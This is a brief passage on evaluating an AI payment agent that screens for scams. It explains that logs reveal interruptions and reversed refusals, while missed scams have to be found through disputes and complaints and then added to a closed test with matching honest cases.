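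The company can use these logs to measure how often the agent interrupts people and how often people reverse its refusals. The logs are much less useful for finding missed scams, because a successful scam looks like an ordinary payment. The company has to find those through disputed charges, calls from unpaid suppliers and similar complaints, then add each one to the closed test along with a matching honest case.
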